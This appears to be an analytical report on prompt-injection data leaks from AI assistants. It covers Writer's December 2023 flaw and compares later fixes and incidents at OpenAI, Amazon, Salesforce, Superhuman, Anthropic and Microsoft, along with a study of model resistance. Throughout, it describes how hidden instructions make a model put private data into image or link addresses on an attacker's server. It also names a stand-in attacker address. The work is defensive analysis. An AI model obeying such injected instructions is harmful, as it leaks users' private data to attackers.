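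Writer also asks researchers not to discuss any flaw outside the program without its express consent, even after it has fixed the flaw. The rule has no time limit and no exception for reports that Writer rejects. A researcher in PromptArmor's position who followed it would have had to keep quiet about an attack that Writer did not regard as a security issue and had no plans to stop. Companies have good reasons to want secrecy while they prepare a fix, but OpenAI and Notion found out about real flaws in their products only because PromptArmor published them. A researcher who obeyed Writer's rule could not have corrected a mistaken rejection by publishing the flaw.

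In July 2026, The Hacker News reported an account-takeover flaw in Writer that is unrelated to the December 2023 data leak. Sand Security found the flaw and named it WriteOut, and Writer patched it before the report appeared.

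## Whether removing images and links was enough

Writer changed its chat within four days of publication. On 18 December 2023, Willison updated his post to say that Writer appeared to have blocked the ways of getting data out. A day later, PromptArmor added that the chat no longer rendered Markdown images or clickable links. Neither explained how Writer made the change, and Willison hoped the company would publish details of its protections.

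The change stops the leak that PromptArmor demonstrated. The model may still write the code for an image with a client's Social Security number in the address, but the chat no longer turns that code into a picture, so the browser doesn't contact the attacker's server. The change also stops both of the "learn more" attacks. It works however the attacker words the hidden text, because it doesn't depend on the model detecting the attack. But customers could no longer see pictures in an answer or click through to a source, which is inconvenient in a tool for writing reports.

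Nothing in either account suggests that the model stopped following instructions in hidden text. An attacker who can't extract data can still use such instructions to add false claims to the model's answers. For instance, a supplier's web page could tell the model to describe a rival's product as unsafe, and the user would read that claim in the summary they requested. PromptArmor also warned that an attacker could use the model to talk users into revealing private information. A page can also affect later answers. In Rehberger's attack on Bing Chat, described by Embrace The Red, the malicious image appeared only after two more turns of conversation.

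### Taking away one part of the trifecta

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) lists Writer among more than a dozen products with the same kind of flaw. Willison notes that almost all the vendors fixed it promptly, usually by blocking the route the data took out. He reasons that because no known defence works every time, a careful developer should assume that some injections will succeed. The product is then safe from data theft only if it lacks at least one of private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out. In his notes on other leaks, Willison argues that removing one of the three is the only reliable defence and that the way out is generally the easiest to remove.

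Images and clickable links were easier for Writer to give up than access to files. An assistant that couldn't read a company's files would have been of little use to the company. Blocking web pages would not have kept out all hidden instructions, because strangers write some of those files.

OpenAI instead keeps images and links, checks each address before loading it, and adds other defences in case the check fails. A third approach relies mainly on training the model to resist injection, which would also help against false content. Willison's argument covers only data theft, and it is harder to apply when a product can send data out in many ways.

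### How other vendors closed the channel

Microsoft kept images in Bing Chat but restricted where they could come from. After the fix in June 2023, Rehberger found a Content Security Policy that allowed images from a few named Bing servers, which the chatbot needed for pictures it created. His earlier attacks no longer worked, though he thought Microsoft might have made other changes. Writer's policy worked the same way, but an attacker can't simply rent a server under one of Bing's names, as PromptArmor could under CloudFront's.

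Amazon's fix was closer to Writer's. Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business* describes an attack on a workplace assistant that Amazon had just released as a preview. Rehberger uploaded a text file containing an instruction to show a "Sign In" link whose address contained a summary of the user's messages. He reported this on 4 December 2023. By 29 December, Amazon was replacing addresses in answers with "[URL not displayed]". This leaves the user nothing to click or copy, but it also removes harmless addresses, so users who want to check a source have to find it themselves.

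In December 2023, OpenAI added a check against data leaks through images, having declined to act that April. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, the ChatGPT website sent each image's address to an OpenAI server before displaying the image. If the server classified the address as unsafe, the browser did not request the image. OpenAI did not publish its criteria, and some addresses on arbitrary domains still passed, so an attacker could leak small amounts of data, though slowly and rather conspicuously. The check ran in the website's code, so OpenAI would have to build it separately into each app, and the iPhone app did not have it. Writer would have had to do the same for any other place it displayed the chat's answers.

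*Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (OpenAI, 2026) describes a clearer rule. ChatGPT automatically loads a page or image only if a crawler has already recorded its exact address. The crawler is a program that explores the web much as a search engine does, recording public addresses without access to users' conversations or accounts. If the address isn't in its records, the system either tells the model to try another site or warns the user that the address may contain information from the conversation.

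In the example of the bookkeeper whose file contained Ana Ruiz's salary, the crawler might well have seen `attacker.example/trends.png`, and the attacker would learn very little from a request for it. The crawler would not have seen the same address with Ruiz's record attached, because nobody had published it before the conversation. The rule would therefore have blocked PromptArmor's image on Writer, even though CloudFront was on the list of approved domains, and ordinary public pictures would still have loaded. The rule requires an index of the web, which OpenAI has and a business writing company probably doesn't.

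OpenAI argues that strict lists of approved sites cause so many warnings that people learn to click through them. Its own rule must cause some too, since a new page or a private company document may not be in the index. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger calls the rule a significant improvement but notes that the model's choice among known addresses can still reveal a little information. He suggests preventing an agent from opening the same address twice in a session. He also worries that some of OpenAI's developers won't know about the check and will leave it out of new features. A company can easily overlook one place where it displays a model's answers, as happened with the log viewer that displayed a blocked image to developers in November 2025.

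### Approved domains that outsiders could use

Strangers could use Writer's approved domain from the start, whereas one approved by Salesforce, which makes customer management software, became unsafe later. Salesforce's Agentforce product lets staff ask an AI agent about sales enquiries, some of which arrive through a public web form. Researchers at the security firm Noma used the form to submit an enquiry containing instructions. When an employee asked about that enquiry, the agent collected the email addresses of other potential customers and wrote them into an image's web address.

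Salesforce had a policy against images from untrusted sites, but Willison explains that its list of trusted sites still included a domain whose registration had expired. The researchers registered the domain and received the data. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* gives the flaw a severity score of 9.4. Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* reports that by 8 September 2025, Salesforce had secured the domain again and begun to stop its agents from sending output to addresses not on a trusted list. The new control covers more than images, but Salesforce still has to keep the list up to date.

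PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack that used an approved domain that had not expired. Superhuman, an email application, allowed images from `docs.google.com`, where Google also hosts its online forms. A form's address can include answers, which Google records as soon as a browser requests the address. A malicious email contained an instruction to put the user's other emails into such an address and present it as an image. The attack worked when the user asked for a summary of recent mail, even if they had not opened the malicious email. The researchers obtained parts of more than 40 emails in one answer.

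PromptArmor reported this on a Friday night in December 2025. Superhuman switched off the vulnerable features on Monday and deployed its first lasting patch a day later. It released further fixes until the day before publication in January, partly because PromptArmor had found related flaws elsewhere in the company's products.

Even a vendor's own domain can be unsafe. In January 2026, PromptArmor showed that Claude Cowork, Anthropic's assistant for office tasks, could upload a user's files to an attacker's account on Anthropic's service, which was on the list of approved destinations. All these lists recorded which domains the vendor trusted. To stop a leak, a vendor also has to know who can read the data sent to each domain, and that can change without the vendor doing anything.

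### Agents have more ways out

Writer's 2023 chat displayed text to one user in one window. An agent, a model that can use other software on a user's behalf, may send messages, open pages and save files. Each of these actions can leak data, even if the chat window displays no images.

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* gives an example from May 2026. Copilot Cowork, an agent in Microsoft's office software, asks permission before sending emails or Teams messages, except those to the user it is working for. Although the user is allowed to see the data, these messages can leak it because they can contain an image from an outside server. When the user opens the message in Outlook or Teams, the image request goes to the attacker.

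Copilot Cowork can create download links that work for anyone who has them, so an attacker who receives a link can fetch the whole file. The request needs to contain only the link, which avoids the limit on how much text fits into an image's address. The injection took up five lines of an 81-line "skill", a file of instructions that a user uploads to teach the agent a task. PromptArmor advises companies to limit which files their staff can access. Companies can also block downloads, but then employees can't print those files or open them in Microsoft's desktop applications.

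An agent with a tool for reading web pages can leak data without displaying anything. Reading a page means sending a request to its server, so the tool that brings in untrusted content can also send private data out. Anthropic recognised this when it designed Claude's web fetch tool. The tool could open only exact addresses that the user had typed or that a web search had returned, which prevented the model from writing private data into a new address.

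*How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) discusses a gap in this rule. Claude could also follow links on pages it had already opened. The researcher Ayush Paul built a site on which Claude's choice of links revealed what it knew about the user, including the user's name, home city and employer, without Claude writing an address of its own. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally and closed the gap by no longer letting the tool follow links from pages it had fetched. The change also meant that honest users could no longer have Claude follow a reference from one page to the next.

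### How well models resist

If models reliably ignored instructions in web pages, these restrictions would matter much less. *The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) tested how reliably some models did so. The researchers gave an agent a made-up secret, told it to send the secret only to one trusted server, and asked it to summarise a web page. The agent's tools only recorded what it tried to do. For each attack, the researchers ran the task with a clean page and with a poisoned one. They counted the attack as successful only if the agent leaked the secret with the poisoned page but not with the clean one.

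The six models were fairly old by the time the study appeared in August 2026. Two were OpenAI's GPT-4o and GPT-4o mini, and the others were small models with public weights. GPT-4o never leaked the secret in 200 trials covering ten types of openly worded attack. The researchers then rewrote one type so that the leak looked like a routine technical step. GPT-4o leaked the secret in 40% of these trials, and two of the rewritten versions worked every time. Four of the other five models also became much more likely to leak. The fifth had already leaked fairly often and hardly changed.

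When Rahman and Kim paraphrased one effective page five times, the success rates ranged from 0% to 100%. An attacker who tried three of these paraphrases would have had about a 96% chance of success with at least one. Inventing a new attack was harder, and thirteen ideas all failed, over 130 trials. The main danger is therefore an attacker who already has a working page and keeps rewording it.

In Rahman and Kim's tests, SecAlign, a published method of training a model to ignore instructions in the material it reads, helped against familiar attacks. It stopped a standard injection in all 20 trials, while the same model without the training obeyed every time. Against the reworded attacks, the trained model leaked in 32.5% of trials and the untrained one in 21.2%, a difference small enough to be chance. SecAlign's developers had not trained it for agents that use tools, so the test shows a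 limit on where the method works, not that it fails in the uses it was trained for.

Two restrictions outside the model reduced the leaks to zero in these tests. One was a list of permitted destinations, which assumes that only trusted people can read what arrives there. That was false at Writer, Salesforce and Superhuman. The other divided the work between one model that chose the actions without seeing the page and another that summarised the page without seeing the secret. The split system still produced a good summary in nine of ten trials, but the task was easy to divide. PromptArmor's user wanted a single report based on both a client file and a web article, and keeping the two apart would be harder in a product like Writer.

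Rahman and Kim also tried some of their attacks on the ChatGPT product, which did not leak the secret in any of 48 valid trials. They couldn't tell which of its defences was responsible. They checked only whether the secret appeared in ChatGPT's reply, and 48 trials are too few to rule out a true attack success rate of about 7%.

Newer models are not clearly safe either. Anthropic described Claude Mythos 5.1 in a September 2026 system card (a developer's report on a model's abilities and safety) as its most robust model to date on an outside benchmark of indirect injection. Yet PromptArmor's attack on Copilot Cowork had worked in all five trials, and it also worked when the researchers selected Claude Opus 4.7, the more advanced model on offer. That model searched more thoroughly for recent documents and so leaked more of them. Five trials are too few to estimate the attack's success rate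 precisely, since an attack that works 55% of the time would still succeed in all five trials about 5% of the time.

The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code* reports a more serious result from Rehberger. When he asked Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, to summarise a web page, it ran an attacker's code in up to 80% of attempts. Anthropic told him the product was working as designed. Rehberger and PromptArmor both wrote their attacks for particular products, so these rates show what a determined attacker can achieve.

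### What a low rate means when the attacker can retry

If a model resists an attack 99% of the time and each attempt is independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is 1 − 0.99ⁿ, which is about 63% for 100 attempts and 95% for 300. An attacker on Writer could put a page where 300 customers might use it, though they couldn't make one customer summarise it 300 times. They could also test different wordings on their own account first and use the best one.

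In practice the attempts aren't fully independent. If the model recognises a particular wording, it may refuse it every time, and the vendor may notice the failures and block the page. A 1% rate is still much better than 50%, especially for a customer nobody is targeting. But switching off images cuts the chance of a leak through an image to zero on every attempt, so a 1% rate doesn't justify leaving that channel open when a file of salaries could leak.

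Removing images and links doesn't stop false content, because it reaches the user in the answer itself, and a vendor can't block answers without blocking the product. Writer's customers still had to rely on the model to resist hidden instructions that would falsify a summary, and on their own willingness to check the source.
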